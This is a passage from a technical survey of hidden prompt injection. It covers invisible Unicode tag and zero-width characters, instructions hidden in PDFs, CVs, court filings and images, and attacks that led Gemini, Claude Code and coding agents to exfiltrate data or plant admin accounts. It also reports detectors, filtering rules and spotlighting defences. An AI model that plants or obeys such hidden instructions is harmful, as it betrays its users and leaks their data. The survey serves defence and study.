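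Later that year Rehberger used the technique in an attack on Microsoft 365 Copilot that hid personal data in a link. Microsoft had fixed the flaw by August 2024, according to Language Log's *Invisible text via Unicode tag characters*. In 2025, Embrace The Red's *Sneaky Bits* reported that a few vendors had also added fixes to the APIs through which other programs reach their models. It warned that other invisible Unicode characters can hold data, so a filter for the Tags block alone is incomplete.

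The security company FireTail tested six assistants with invisible text. Gemini, Grok and DeepSeek read it, while ChatGPT, Copilot and Claude seemed to remove it. *ASCII Smuggling in Google Gemini*, by the researcher vict0ni, describes a calendar invitation whose visible title was just "Meeting". Hidden text made Gemini tell the user that the meeting was optional, and changed the organiser's name and meeting link that Gemini reported. This worked even if the victim had not accepted the invitation.

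FireTail reported this to Google on 18 September 2025 and received a "no action" reply, according to Cyber Security News. Google's reasons, quoted in BGR's *Google Has No Plans To Fix This Terrifying Gemini Security Vulnerability*, were that the attack "can only result in social engineering" (tricking a person) and that a fix would not make users less prone to such attacks.

Google's argument is reasonable for the calendar demonstration, which does no harm until someone believes the false details. But the user is unlikely to notice the trick, because the calendar displays one text and Gemini reports another. The argument is also much weaker for an agent that can send mail or run commands, since it could follow an invisible instruction before anyone could be fooled. FireTail (2026) found in January that a related method, which hides text in emoji, worked on Gemini and Grok but not on the other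 four assistants it tested.

### How tool access changes compliance

*Reverse CAPTCHA* (Graves, 2026) measured how often models follow invisible instructions. The test used 30 trivia questions, each with an invisible instruction to give a particular wrong answer. Half of the instructions used tag characters and half used zero-width characters, which are outside the Tags block. Graves ran five models with and without a tool for running Python code, and graded 8,308 answers, including some to questions with no hidden text. The table gives the share of answers that followed the hidden instruction.

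| Model | Without the tool | With the tool |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4 | 16.9% | 71.2% |
| Claude Opus 4 | 6.7% | 51.1% |
| Claude Haiku 4.5 | 0.8% | 49.2% |
| GPT-5.2 | 0.1% | 20.6% |
| GPT-4o-mini | 0.1% | 1.6% |

The tool matters because it lets the model write a short program to turn the invisible characters back into letters, which it would otherwise have to work out unaided.

These averages overstate the danger to ordinary users. In three of the four test conditions, the system prompt told the model that the text contained a hidden instruction, and in two of those three it also explained how to decode it. An attacker who controls only a web page or an email can't add such hints to the system prompt. With no hint, compliance was at most 1.1% without the tool and between 0% and 11% with it. The higher figures are relevant when an attacker can also influence the agent's configuration,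 such as through a tool description.

Claude Opus 4 always followed the instructions written in tag characters when it had both the tool and a hint, but GPT-5.2 almost never did. Graves suspects the cause is a difference between the companies' tokenizers. The test can't rule out a filter at OpenAI's API that deletes tag characters before they reach the model.

In FireTail's results, Claude seemed to remove tags in September 2025, but in February 2026 Embrace The Red's *Scary Agent Skills* described an attack on Claude Code with the same characters. Rehberger had added an invisible instruction to a copy of a skill that OpenAI publishes. With automatic approval of commands switched on, Claude Code printed the requested phrase and ran a command. On 10 February Claude Code began to detect the characters and refuse, though Rehberger could not tell whether Anthropic had made a deliberate fix. The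 claude.ai website had no such protection for skills the day before. Developers therefore have to test their own products, because a good result for one product is weak evidence about another that uses the same company's models.

Invisible characters are hard to notice, but they don't seem to make a model more likely to follow instructions. In *Poisoned Skills*, Manjusha and Emani (2026) found that zero-width characters did not raise the success rate of harmful requests to seven open-weight models.

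Actual attacks of this kind appear to be rare. Nakibly and Babo found invisible characters in 1,777 of two million READMEs and decoded all of them. Almost all were legitimate, and only one README used them to instruct visiting agents, which were asked to praise a contributor's work. But they checked issues and pull requests, where attackers were most active, only for HTML comments, so the study can't show how common invisible characters are there. Embrace The Red also scanned two public skill collections and found nothing that looked malicious.

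### Removing, rejecting or displaying them

Removing the whole Tags block is easy and stops this form of hidden text. It also turns the flag emoji of England, Scotland and Wales into plain black flags, which few businesses will mind.

Removing every zero-width character does more damage. Persian uses the zero-width non-joiner inside ordinary words to stop two letters from connecting, so deleting it changes the spelling. Several Indian scripts use joiners and non-joiners to select the right letter shapes. Many emoji also depend on the zero-width joiner, and a family emoji can appear as separate people without it. Graves therefore recommends filtering the patterns that hidden messages use and leaving single characters alone.

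Another option is to reject the whole message, which AWS offers as a setting in Bedrock. This leaves no doubt about what the model received, but a customer who adds a Welsh flag to a complaint may get no answer. Rejection makes more sense for skill files and AGENTS.md, because they rarely need flags and their authors can correct them.

Software could also make the invisible characters visible. The linguist Mark Liberman, writing on Language Log, argued that browsers would be safer if they displayed tag characters as gibberish. This would help people who review code or approve an agent's actions, but it wouldn't protect an agent that reads a message before any person does. An application that handles text from strangers therefore still has to remove the characters.

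### A rule that keeps the flags

An application can remove hidden tag text without losing the three flags:

1. Find each black flag (U+1F3F4) that is followed directly by the tag letters gbeng, gbsct or gbwls and then the end mark (U+E007F). Keep these sequences whole.
2. Delete every other character from U+E0000 to U+E007F.
3. Record how many characters the rule deleted and where the text came from.

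Suppose a message about a football match contains the items below.

| In the message | Characters from the Tags block | Result |
|---|---|---|
| The words "Kick-off at 3 pm" | 0 | Unchanged |
| The flag of England | 6 | All kept |
| The word "hello" in tag letters after the full stop | 5 | All deleted |
| A black flag followed by "hello" in tag letters and an end mark | 6 | Tags deleted, black flag kept |

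The rule keeps 6 of the 17 tag characters and deletes 11. It lists the three flags exactly because a looser rule that accepted any tags after a black flag would let the second "hello" through, as the last row shows. The exact list loses a few rarely used regional flags, such as that of Texas, but most devices can't draw them.

The rule should run after all other decoding, just before the text goes to the model. In some programming languages, one pass may not be enough. Java stores each tag character as two halves, and deleting one character can bring two stray halves together to form a new one. AWS therefore also deletes stray halves and repeats the process until the text stops changing.

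Zero-width characters need a separate rule. An application can keep single joiners and non-joiners between letters and inside emoji, and flag long runs of them, which normal writing doesn't contain. Developers should test both rules on real Persian and Hindi text and on hidden messages. They can test the hidden messages with garak, an open testing tool. *Ascii Smuggling*, from garak, describes its probes for tags and other invisible characters.

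## Checking PDFs and images for text people cannot see

### Why a PDF has two texts

A web page or Markdown file contains its words mostly in reading order, and the software that displays it calculates their positions. A PDF instead contains instructions for drawing particular shapes at particular positions, and it need not record which shapes form a word or which paragraph comes first. To extract the text, a program collects the character codes from these instructions, looks up the letter for each code and guesses the reading order. The text a model receives is therefore produced separately from the page a person sees.

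The underlying text can even be in a different order from the text on the printed page. In the algebra quiz described earlier, Howard swapped two questions in the underlying text without changing the printed order. Claude and Codex both answered in the printed order. They may have looked at an image of the page or followed the question numbers.

White or tiny letters hide text in a PDF much as they do on a web page. *PhantomLint* (Murray, 2025) also describes how people can misuse features specific to documents. The table lists four of them.

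| Feature | Ordinary use | How it separates the two texts |
|---|---|---|
| Layers | Switching parts of a map or plan on and off | The viewer doesn't draw a layer that is off, but its text stays in the file |
| Page boundaries | Trimming the margins that a printer needs | Text outside the boundary stays in the file |
| Text modes | Making scanned pages searchable | One mode places letters on the page without drawing them |
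| Embedded fonts | Supplying the shapes of the letters | A font can draw the wrong shape for a letter, or no shape at all |

A rule against any one of these features would reject many harmless files, because the features also have ordinary uses. For example, a rule against invisible text would flag every searchable scan, which is a picture of a page with the recognised words placed over it as invisible text.

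Altered fonts, which show the reader a different word from the one the extractor returns, are the hardest to notice. The text can be black, of normal size and in the middle of the page, so checking colours and positions doesn't reveal it.

Extraction programs also differ in which text they extract. In Murray's tests, a common extraction tool skipped text on a switched-off layer and text outside the outermost page boundary, but ChatGPT could read both. A developer who checks documents with one extractor and uses another to supply text to the model could approve a document without checking all the text the model receives.

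### Papers, CVs and court filings

In July 2025 the newspaper Nikkei Asia found research papers with hidden instructions for any AI reviewer to give a favourable verdict. The papers were on arXiv, a site where scientists post papers before formal publication. They came from 14 institutions in eight countries, according to Search Engine Journal's *Prompt Injections Just Proved Something SEO Has Known For 25 Years* (2026). Zhicheng Lin, who analysed the case, identified 18 such manuscripts. The organisers of ICML 2025, a large machine-learning conference, found similar text in papers they had accepted. Murray found more examples, including a paper that seemed to be under review at the time, and notified the editors.

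Some of the researchers responsible said they had set a trap for reviewers who secretly used AI. Lin rejected this defence because a trap would tell the AI not to review the paper, whereas these instructions asked for praise. One preprint that Murray found did contain a real trap. It asked AI reviewers to include a particular harmless phrase and change nothing else, so that the phrase would reveal the use of AI.

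Federico Torrielli and colleagues at the University of Turin tested both kinds of instruction on 100 real papers and collected 42,000 outputs from ChatGPT and Gemini. Search Engine Journal reports that instructions to write a favourable review, to refuse the task or to send the reviewer to an outside web page each worked more than 98% of the time. An instruction to leave an invisible marker in the review worked 94% of the time on ChatGPT and 88% on Gemini. The article mentions no fix by OpenAI or Google.

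These rates are much higher than Howard's result would suggest, since both assistants there ignored the odd requests. A request about the tone of a review closely resembles the user's own task, which may explain part of the difference, but it can't explain why the models also obeyed instructions to refuse. For a conference, the results mean that markers can catch careless reviewers and that an AI review of an unchecked PDF is worth very little. A conference that uses markers also has to exempt them from its own search for hidden text.

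Job applicants hide text too. Mohan Zhang and colleagues examined 196,682 real CVs and found hidden injections in about 1% of them. More than 90% of these were blocks of keywords with no instruction, presumably added to make the applicant look like a better match. Murray's collection, which came from searches for typical instructions, has more blatant cases. Most of its CVs contained instructions to recommend the candidate, but at least one contained a request for a story about Shrek.

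People have also hidden text in court filings. In July 2026 a man suing a medical practice in Connecticut filed a motion containing instructions to AI in three-point white text. The judge was working on paper, and the court noticed that the filings had more white space than usual. The man called the text an "audit" of whether the court used AI. The judge treated the attempt as misconduct even though it had failed, and barred him from filing electronically. SC Media's *Man banned from electronic filing after hiding AI prompt injection* (2026) describes this as probably the first sanction of its kind in the United States. In Brazil, a court's own AI flagged hidden instructions to give a filing only superficial scrutiny. The lawyers were fined $16,000, according to Tom's Hardware's *Brazilian lawyers busted for attempting to manipulate court's AI with prompt injection*.

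### Comparing the extracted text with the drawn page

Odd white space is an unreliable clue, and text on a switched-off layer leaves none. PhantomLint, the open-source tool that Murray built, instead compares the two texts directly. It works on PDFs and web pages in five steps:

1. It extracts the text in blocks, each about a paragraph long, and records where each block lies on the page. For a PDF, it first widens the page boundaries and switches on every layer so that the extraction misses nothing.
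2. It looks for suspicious text by comparing short stretches of each block with ten sample phrases, such as a request for a positive review. A small language model scores how close they are in meaning, so the wording need not match exactly. Blocks with no suspicious text go no further.
3. It draws the part of the page that the suspicious block occupies, and nothing else.
4. It reads this drawing with optical character recognition (OCR), which turns pictures of letters into text.
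5. It lists the extracted words that OCR did not find, and raises an alarm if any of them belong to the suspicious text.

The last step can be written as a formula. If T is the set of extracted words, O the set that OCR read and S the suspicious part of T, then the tool raises an alarm when

S ∩ (T − O) ≠ ∅,

which means that at least one suspicious word is missing from the drawing.

Suppose an applicant's CV has a 20-word block in which he describes a job in 12 black words and asks for a recommendation in eight white ones. Text extraction returns all 20 words, but OCR returns only the 12 black ones. The tool raises an alarm because the eight missing words are also suspicious. If the applicant had written the request in black, OCR would have returned all 20 words and the tool would not have raised an alarm. For the same reason, an article that openly quotes prompt injections doesn't trigger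 one.

The method doesn't depend on how someone hid the text, because white letters, a covering picture and an altered font all produce the same mismatch. Step 3 uses a small drawing because the same phrase might be visible elsewhere on the page. If the tool read the whole page, the visible copy would make the hidden one look visible too.

OCR is an imperfect substitute for a human reader here. It can read nearly white letters on a white background that no person would notice, and the tool would then count them as visible. PhantomLint therefore blurs low-contrast areas before running OCR. A similar check also needs to draw the page as a normal viewer would show it. Otherwise, text from the widened margins and switched-off layers could appear in the drawing and be counted as visible.

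Murray tested the tool on 3,402 documents.

| Documents | Number | Alarms |
|---|---|---|
| Synthetic files with hidden instructions | 26 | 26 |
| Real documents with hidden instructions | 113 | 113 |
| Real documents with visible instructions | 6 | 0 |
| Papers accepted at ICML 2025 | 3,257 | 3, all false |

The synthetic files covered nine ways of hiding text, including an altered font. In the 113 real documents, the tool always found at least part of the hidden instruction, but not always all of it. The three false alarms came from OCR errors, two on letters outside the English alphabet and one on very small print.

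The perfect score on real documents overstates how well the tool works, because Murray found most of these documents by searching Google for typical injection phrases, and the tool's ten sample phrases are of the same kind. Step 2 would probably filter out hidden text without such wording, like the extra equation in Howard's quiz or the keyword blocks in most of the CVs, so the tool would miss it. A developer could skip that step and compare every block, but then any OCR error could cause a false alarm.

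Murray inspected the three ICML papers that the tool flagged but had no independent check of the other 3,254, so this part of the test measures false alarms but not misses.

### The daily workload

Murray's false alarm rate of about 0.092% comes from the ICML papers alone, as 3 ÷ 3,257. For an organisation that receives 10,000 clean documents a day, the expected number of false alarms is

10,000 × 3 ÷ 3,257 ≈ 9.

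One person can easily review nine documents a day. That estimate is based on only three errors, though, and its 95% confidence interval runs from about 2 to 27 false alarms a day. The rate could also change with the type of document. Judging by the OCR errors, more documents in other languages would probably mean more false alarms.

Whether nine false alarms is a lot also depends on the number of real cases. If the 10,000 documents are CVs and 1% have hidden text, as in Zhang's study, about 100 a day contain hidden text. Fewer than 10 of those contain an actual instruction, which is what PhantomLint looks for by default. The reviewer would then see roughly as many false alarms as real cases. That is still far better than the classifier results on GitHub described earlier, where nearly all the supposed attacks were false alarms.

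Computing time may be the bigger obstacle. PhantomLint took an average of 68 seconds for each ICML paper on a 2021 laptop. At that speed, 10,000 papers would take about 190 hours, or about a day on eight such laptops. Short documents take less time, and a faster OCR program would presumably help. An assistant that has to answer questions about an attachment within seconds can't wait a minute for the check, so the check would have to run when the message arrives.

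### What a detector loses when a PDF becomes plain text

Many systems convert a PDF to plain text before checking it for injections. Thienpreecha and Subramanian (2026) argue in *CrackedPDFs* that this discards the best evidence. Plain text no longer shows where a sentence was, what colour it had or whether the PDF viewer drew it at all. A sentence that looks harmless as text can be highly suspicious if it lies outside the page.

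The researchers generated 29,322 PDFs from 4,983 base documents to train and test detectors. All were artificial one-page files, such as invoices, memos and course handouts. A third contained hidden instructions. The rest were clean originals and "benign confounders", harmless counterparts of the injected files. The confounders make the test harder, because a detector can't succeed just by recognising how the software produced the injected files. The researchers kept all versions of a document in the same set, so no detector was trained on one version and tested on another.

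The test set had 973 injected files and 1,946 harmless ones. Prompt Guard, a classifier from Meta that received only the extracted text, caught about 25% of the injected files. A hybrid detector that used the text and the structure of the PDF missed only two injected files and wrongly flagged 78 harmless ones (4%).

Nearly all of the hybrid's 78 false alarms must have been on confounders. On the injected files and their confounders alone, it was right 95.9% of the time, which means about 80 errors, and two of those were the missed injections. It therefore flagged about 8% of the confounders and almost none of the clean originals. At 10,000 documents a day, it could raise hardly any false alarms or several hundred, depending on how many harmless files resemble the confounders.

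Checking the structure may not explain all of the gap between 25% and nearly 100%, because the researchers also trained the hybrid, but not Prompt Guard, on files from the same generator as the test files. The two detectors that used structure alone also did poorly. The better one scored 0.651 on F1, a measure from 0 to 1 that combines missed cases and false alarms, while the hybrid scored 0.960. The results support combining the two kinds of evidence more than they support using either one alone.

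Another detector, which used only word patterns in the extracted text, got a perfect score. The researchers discounted this result because the detector had relied partly on marker words that their own software had put around every hidden instruction. They removed these words from the text before giving it to the hybrid.

The hybrid had trouble with unfamiliar attacks. When the researchers left one type of hidden text out of the training, the hybrid rated the injected file as more suspicious than its confounder in only 42% of pairs, while random guessing would give 50%. The researchers did not test scanned documents, real-world PDFs or attackers who adapt to the detector. PhantomLint's comparison doesn't need training examples of each hiding method, but its phrase list determines where the comparison is applied.

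Developers should check the original file for hidden text and pass the findings along with the extracted text, because no later filter can recover positions and colours that the converter has discarded.

### Text in images that people overlook

A PDF may give the model words that don't appear on the displayed page, while an image may contain visible words that people fail to notice. *AI 黑魔法（10）* (Vivian, 2026) describes an example of the latter from October 2023, soon after chat assistants became able to read images. Riley Goodside gave one an image that looked blank but contained a message in almost the same white as the background. The message instructed the model to mention a sale at the cosmetics chain Sephora, and the model did so.

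The same weakness later appeared in Perplexity's Comet, a browser that can act for its user. People can take a screenshot of a web page in Comet and ask questions about it. In *Unseeable prompt injections in screenshots*, Chaikin and Sahib showed that Comet read faint text in such a screenshot and treated it as a command to use its browser tools. They work for Brave, which makes a competing browser. They reported the flaw to Perplexity on 1 October 2025 and published it on 21 October, without saying whether Perplexity had fixed it.

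Coding agents also encounter images, since many projects contain logos and screenshots. *Visual prompt injection vulnerability bypasses AI guardrails* (Davison, 2026) describes InkJect, an attack that the AI security company DeepKeep reported in July 2026. In one test, a developer asked a model to add a simple information page to a website. An image in a public repository contained hidden instructions, and the model also built a login system with an administrator account that the attacker could use.

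DeepKeep tested GPT-5.2, GPT-5.4 Mini, Claude Sonnet 4.6 and Claude Opus 4.5, and all four followed the hidden instructions, according to Antipov's *Пустая на вид картинка — полноценная команда для ИИ* (2026). Both articles rely on DeepKeep's account, and neither gives the number of attempts. DeepKeep reported the flaw to OpenAI and Anthropic, but the articles mention no fix. TechNews' *惡意程式碼不用藏在程式裡* (2026) describes a similar demonstration, in which an image in a pull request was enough to make a coding assistant leak a project's secrets.

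InkJect also exposes a weakness in a common defence, which is to extract the text from an image with OCR and search it for instructions. DeepKeep found that models could read text that was too faint or distorted for OCR, so these scanners can miss instructions that the model can read. PhantomLint has the opposite problem, because it uses OCR to approximate what a person can see, and OCR can detect text that a person would miss. An image scanner should instead use a model at least as capable as the one it protects, though that model could also end up following the hidden instructions.

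### How often faint text works

Koide, Nakano and Chiba (2026), in *Clouding the Mirror*, measured the effect on AI systems that detect phishing sites. These systems are an obvious target because the criminal controls everything on the page that the model inspects. In one experiment, the models received screenshots with faint text and had to either decide whether the page asked for login details or name the brand it displayed. Each test used only 40 pages, and the attacks succeeded on one to ten of them (2.5% to 25%), depending on the model and the task.

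A larger experiment gave the models the page's source code and URL as well as a screenshot. The attacker's text generally worked better in comments, metadata and other places that visitors never see than in the screenshot. Faint text worked better on models that were better at reading images, so this risk may grow as models' vision improves.

Koide and colleagues counted an attack as successful whenever the system failed to report phishing, even if the model refused to answer or produced unusable output. That is fair for a phishing detector, since a criminal benefits from any failure. It would exaggerate the danger to an assistant that reads email, where a garbled answer does far less harm than a forwarded mailbox. Liu and Lao (2026) make a similar criticism in *VisInject* of research on pixel changes too small for people to see. Studies of these attacks often report success rates of 60%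 to 80%, but the figures combine cases where the answer only changed with cases where the attacker got the intended result.

Koide and colleagues also tested a defence that marks page content as untrusted, supplies the real web addresses of known brands and checks the format of the answer. In the larger experiment, it cut the attack success rate from 39.9% to 0.3% on GPT-5, but only from 84.7% to 61.7% on Llama 4 Maverick. With the smallest model, Gemma 3, the defence caused the system to label a quarter of 250 legitimate websites as phishing. The researchers looked for such attacks on real phishing sites and found no clear examples.

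### Images that change when software shrinks them

A person can inspect an image closely and still miss text that reaches the model. Many applications shrink large images before passing them to a model, which combines several pixels into one. If an image goes from 4,000 to 1,000 pixels on each side, each new pixel replaces 16 old ones. An attacker can arrange the old pixels so that they look like ordinary dark areas at full size but form readable words in the smaller copy.

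Trail of Bits' *Weaponizing image scaling against production AI systems* (2025) demonstrated this on Google's Gemini CLI, a coding agent. When a user uploaded a harmless-looking picture, the agent emailed data from the user's Google Calendar to the attacker. The agent didn't ask first because the connection to the outside service came with automatic approval on. The method also worked on Gemini's website and programming interface, Vertex AI Studio, Google Assistant on an Android phone and the Genspark agent. Vertex AI Studio showed the user the full-size image while the model received the small one. Trail of Bits did not report whether any of these companies had fixed the flaw.

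Trail of Bits advises developers to limit the size of uploads rather than shrink images. If an application must change an image, it should show the user the version the model will receive. A preview helps someone who uploads a single picture and looks at it, but it does little when an agent opens hundreds of images on its own. Trail of Bits therefore considers it more important that text in an image can never trigger a sensitive action without the user's explicit approval.

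### What a screenshot removes

Giving a model a screenshot instead of extracted text removes much of the hidden text described so far. Comments, metadata, invisible characters and switched-off layers do not appear in a screenshot. An altered font also loses its effect, because the model sees the same shapes as a human reader. A screenshot would leave out most of the injections in the web census.

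A screenshot preserves faint text, tiny text and words inside photographs, and shrinking an image can make hidden text visible. Screenshots and photographs are also harder to check. PhantomLint compares extracted text with an image of the rendered page, but these files have no separate text to compare. A reviewer should save the exact image that the model received, after any shrinking or cropping, and examine it with the contrast turned up.

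Systems that give the model both a PDF's extracted text and images of its pages need a further test. Vivian suggests checking which source the model relies on when the extracted text, the OCR result and the image disagree. A developer can do this with a harmless PDF that shows one date on the page and has a different one in its extractable text.

An attacker may not need to hide the instructions. Chaikin and Sahib found that the AI browser Fellou followed visible instructions on a web page as soon as the user asked it to go there. They reported the flaw on 20 August 2025 and did not mention a fix. Comparing the page as displayed with its text would have found no difference, so only a limit on what the browser may do without asking the user could have stopped this attack.

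## Choosing which version of a page the model receives

An agent's developer has to choose a page representation, which is the form in which a page reaches the model. It can be plain text, HTML source, a screenshot or something in between. In a large test with real injections, models followed the injections most often in plain text, even though stripping out the formatting removes the comments, attributes and style rules that so much hidden text depends on.

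### An experiment with real injections

Khodayari and colleagues ran this test on injections from their web census. They picked 100 different injections at random, each on a page of its own, and asked 13 models to summarize the pages in four forms:

- Plain text is what remains after a program removes the HTML tags.
- HTML keeps the tags, attributes, scripts and comments.
- The raw response is the HTML together with the server's headers.
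- A snapshot is a structured outline of the page as a browser rendered it.

This made 5,200 runs. The researchers read every answer to see whether the model had followed the injection instead of doing its task.

| Form | Obeyed | Failed to produce a usable answer | Obeyed, among completed runs |
|---|---|---|---|
| Plain text | 3.9% | 0.7% | 3.9% |
| HTML | 1.1% | 20.3% | 1.4% |
| Snapshot | 1.1% | 3.5% | 1.1% |
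| Raw response | 0.2% | 25.8% | 0.3% |

The last column is a recalculation that excludes failed runs. For HTML it is 1.1 ÷ (1 − 0.203) ≈ 1.4%. Most of the failures happened when a page was too long for the model's context, and a run without a finished answer doesn't show that the model resisted the hidden instructions.

The recalculation assumes that models would have obeyed as often in the failed runs as in the completed ones. They might have obeyed more often, since small models failed most and also obeyed most often. Even so, failures are unlikely to explain the whole gap. The percentages correspond to models obeying in 51 of 1,300 runs with plain text and 14 of 1,300 with HTML. To close the gap, models would have had to obey in 37 of the 264 failed HTML runs, or 14%, and no group of models exceeded 8.0% in any form.

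### Why plain text did worst

Khodayari and colleagues think that converting a page to plain text removes the signs that text was hidden. A model given the HTML can detect that a sentence is inside a comment or has a font size of zero, but in plain text the same sentence looks like any other part of the article.

The results by model size fit this explanation. The three small models obeyed in 8.0% of their plain-text runs, and the other groups in about 2% to 3%. In the other three forms, the models obeyed in only 30 runs, and the published counts imply that 26 of these came from the small models. The medium-sized and closed models obeyed in 17 of 700 plain-text runs and apparently never in the other forms. Larger models may be better at using the signs that HTML preserves.

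But the experiment doesn't rule out two other explanations. One is length, because an injection in a long HTML file is surrounded by far more text than the same injection in a short extract. The other is that some injections never reached the model. An injection in a header, for example, appears only in the raw response. The researchers don't report how many of the 100 injections survived each conversion. If only half survived in plain text, models would have obeyed about 7.8% of the ones they received, and flattening would be more dangerous than the table suggests. The low rate for snapshots may mean only that the browser left out hidden elements, not that the models recognised them. A better test would put the same injection into every form and keep the lengths equal.

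Models can follow hidden instructions even when they receive both a page's full HTML and the text a visitor would see. In *Decoding Latent Attack Surfaces in LLMs*, Verma and Yadav (2025) hid one instruction in each of 140 artificial pages and gave two models both versions. Llama 4 Scout followed the instruction on 41 pages (29%) and Gemma 9B on 22 (16%). Most of the successful instructions were in metadata, comments or transparent text. In one case, a line of metadata led a model to summarize customer reviews in pirate slang.

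The instructions themselves may explain these much higher rates. A model can write like a pirate and still produce the summary the user wanted, but most injections in the census were orders to drop the task. In Howard's algebra quiz, assistants also seemed more likely to act on hidden text that resembled the user's task. Giving the model HTML may therefore help more against crude injections than against those that fit the task.

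The closed models pointed out the injection in 25.1% of their runs and the small models in 4.8%. But in six runs a model identified the injection and still obeyed it, for example by switching to German.

### Newer models and more demanding tasks

Some people who advise websites on search rankings consider the problem solved. Search Engine Land's *Hidden prompt injection* tells marketers that AI "outgrew" the trick and that models now ignore hidden commands. It tested one page, containing the "cabbage" joke mentioned earlier, in ChatGPT and Perplexity. Neither product obeyed, but the article suggests that a filter probably caught the opening phrase.

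Newer models seem to have stopped following blunt demands for nonsense, which make up most of what site owners write, but not instructions that an attacker has fitted to the task. The two closed models in the experiment, GPT-5.4 and ByteDance's Seed 2.0 Mini, obeyed in only 5 of 800 runs. But in the Turin tests, hidden instructions in research papers nearly always worked on ChatGPT and Gemini.

A summarizing task also shows little about whether an injection would change what an agent clicks or buys, because the model has no tools and stops after one answer. *It's a TRAP! Task-Redirecting Agent Persuasion Benchmark for Web Agents* (2025) tested an agent running on Gemini 2.5 Flash in a calendar application. The agent read an outline much like the snapshots above and followed injections in 9 of 104 runs (8.7%). With screenshots added, it followed them in 11 of 105 runs (10.5%), a difference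 that could easily be chance.

These rates are far above the 1.1% for snapshots, but the researchers wrote the injections to be persuasive and made sure the agent received them. The agent was also weak, completing only about one in eight of its ordinary tasks. The 1.1% therefore describes one mix of injections on one task, not the general risk of using snapshots.

### What each form costs

No form of a page is short, complete and free of hidden text. The main options are in the table.

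| What the model receives | Length | What it loses | Hidden text that remains |
|---|---|---|---|
| All text, without tags | Short | Layout, table structure, signs of hiding | Whatever the extractor keeps |
| Visible text only | Short | Image descriptions, screen-reader labels, collapsed sections | Very little |
| HTML | Very long | The page's appearance | Nearly all, with signs of hiding |
| Snapshot | Medium | Much of the layout | Screen-reader labels, some off-screen text |
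| Text marked as untrusted | A few words extra, or up to double | Nothing further | All of it, with a warning |

**Visible text only.** *Hidden-in-Plain-Text* (Guo and Wei, 2026) tested the removal of hidden text in a system that retrieves pages to answer questions, using 6,200 pages in the style of social media and four open models. The models followed injections 24.9% of the time, even though the prompt told them not to follow any instructions in the pages. When the system neutralized hidden elements and risky attributes first, the rate fell to 13.1%.

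The benefit depended on where the injection was. The rate fell from 30.1% to 9.8% for off-screen text and from 27.8% to 11.1% for image descriptions, but it hardly changed for labels that only screen readers announce (9.6% to 9.3%). Zero-width characters needed a separate cleaning step, which cut their rate from 23.2% to 7.8%. With both kinds of cleaning and a rule that every sentence in the answer must cite a passage, the overall rate was 4.7%. About half of the injections that still worked were in plain view, so a filter for hidden text would not remove them.

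Cleaning had little effect on performance in this test. It lowered the share of questions the system could answer by about two percentage points, and removing hidden elements added 31 milliseconds to a typical response time of one second. The drop in answers will be much larger for some tasks, because cleaning can remove information they need. A chart's description may be the only place where its figures appear as text. An icon-only button has no name without its screen-reader label. Shops often put delivery terms in a section that opens only when clicked.

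A developer can recover some of this. The browser that prepares the page can open collapsed sections, as a visitor would, before it extracts the text. The application can pass on image descriptions only when the user asks about an image, and label them as descriptions to keep them distinct from the article's text.

**HTML with its structure.** *HtmlRAG* (2024) argues that HTML is better than plain text for answering questions from retrieved pages, because conversion discards structure such as headings and tables. For agents that operate websites, the better format depends on the model. In *Read More, Think More* (2026), Enomoto, Obara and colleagues gave agents 330 office tasks, such as filling in forms and sorting lists, and provided each page either as HTML or as an accessibility tree, the outline of a page that browsers prepare for screen readers.

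| Model | Tasks completed with the accessibility tree | Tasks completed with HTML |
|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.1, high reasoning setting | 55.8% | 73.3% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 52.4% | 67.0% |
| gpt-oss-120b, high reasoning setting | 46.7% | 38.8% |
| gpt-oss-20b, high reasoning setting | 46.4% | 27.6% |

The HTML included layout details, such as which element lies on top of another, and the stronger models had fewer clicks blocked by a covering element. The weakest model in the table more often tried to use elements that didn't exist. HTML also used far more tokens, about 56,700 per step for GPT-5.1 compared with 6,700 for the accessibility tree.

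HTML thus suits strong models, which work better with it and rarely obeyed the injections in it. Small models are the most easily misled by plain text but also struggle with HTML, so a snapshot is usually the better compromise for them.

Length limits which version of a page any model can receive. *Dripper* (2025) found that 29.3% of 14,000 archived web pages were longer than 32,000 tokens and 21.0% were longer than 128,000. If an application cuts such pages off at a fixed length, the model may miss the answer. If the application sends them whole, some runs will fail.

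Markdown is a compromise between HTML and plain text that keeps headings, lists and simple tables. In tests on financial documents, *A Table Is Worth 64 Tokens* (2026) found that Markdown tables used 8% to 17% fewer tokens than HTML ones, with similar accuracy. But Markdown flattens nested headings and merged cells. It also has no standard way to show that a passage was white or off-screen, so if a converter keeps hidden text, the model can't tell that it was hidden, just as with plain text.

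An accessibility tree lists each element with its role and name, such as a link called "Home". In an example from *Building Browser Agents* (2025), a field for entering a weight took more than 100 lines of HTML but only a few lines of the tree. The tree omits some information an agent needs, so many designs add a screenshot. In Enomoto and colleagues' tests, a screenshot raised GPT-5.1's success rate from 55.8% to 59.7% and added only about 700 tokens.

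A snapshot includes content that a visitor doesn't see, such as labels written for screen readers and, according to *Whose Agent Are You?* (2026), sometimes elements outside the window. Some snapshots record which elements are visible. In an example from *TimeWarp* (2026), the outline of an early Wikipedia home page marks individual headings and links as "visible". A developer could use these marks to remove the unmarked elements, or keep the marks so that the model can tell which elements are visible.

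### What search services already leave out

A developer who relies on a company's web search tool may not be able to choose which version of a page the model receives. In *Fetch, Read, Reuse*, Chen, Canini and colleagues (2026) tested the search tools that OpenAI, Anthropic and xAI offer to developers. They planted secret codes in different parts of their own web pages and asked questions that a model could answer only if it had received the codes.

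None of the three services returned codes placed inside a script, in JSON-LD or in text that a script adds after the page loads. The services apparently delete these parts before the model reads the page. As a side effect, this would block the injections that the census found in JSON-LD and those that Unit 42 saw scripts insert. But it also removes legitimate facts such as prices, and about 40% of the popular home pages that Chen and colleagues checked contain JSON-LD.

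Other omissions have little to do with safety. The xAI tool read only the first half megabyte of a page and didn't tell the user. OpenAI's tool refused files labelled as Markdown, XML or CSV, but accepted the same file when it was labelled as HTML. Anthropic's tool passed on everything in pages of up to two megabytes, and the largest took about 760,000 tokens.

Anthropic also offers a version in which the model writes a small program to select the relevant parts of a page. On 8-kilobyte test pages, this version used 8 to 22 times as many tokens as the basic version and gave no better answers. The questions required codes from all over the page, so there was little to discard. This version may do better on cluttered pages.

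### Marking text as untrusted

Developers can also keep the page's content and tell the model not to trust it. Hines and colleagues proposed this in 2024 and called it spotlighting. *RAISED* (2026) describes a simple version in which the application puts a special mark before and after every tool result. The system prompt explains the marks and tells the model not to follow instructions between them. A more thorough version repeats a warning marker throughout the untrusted text.

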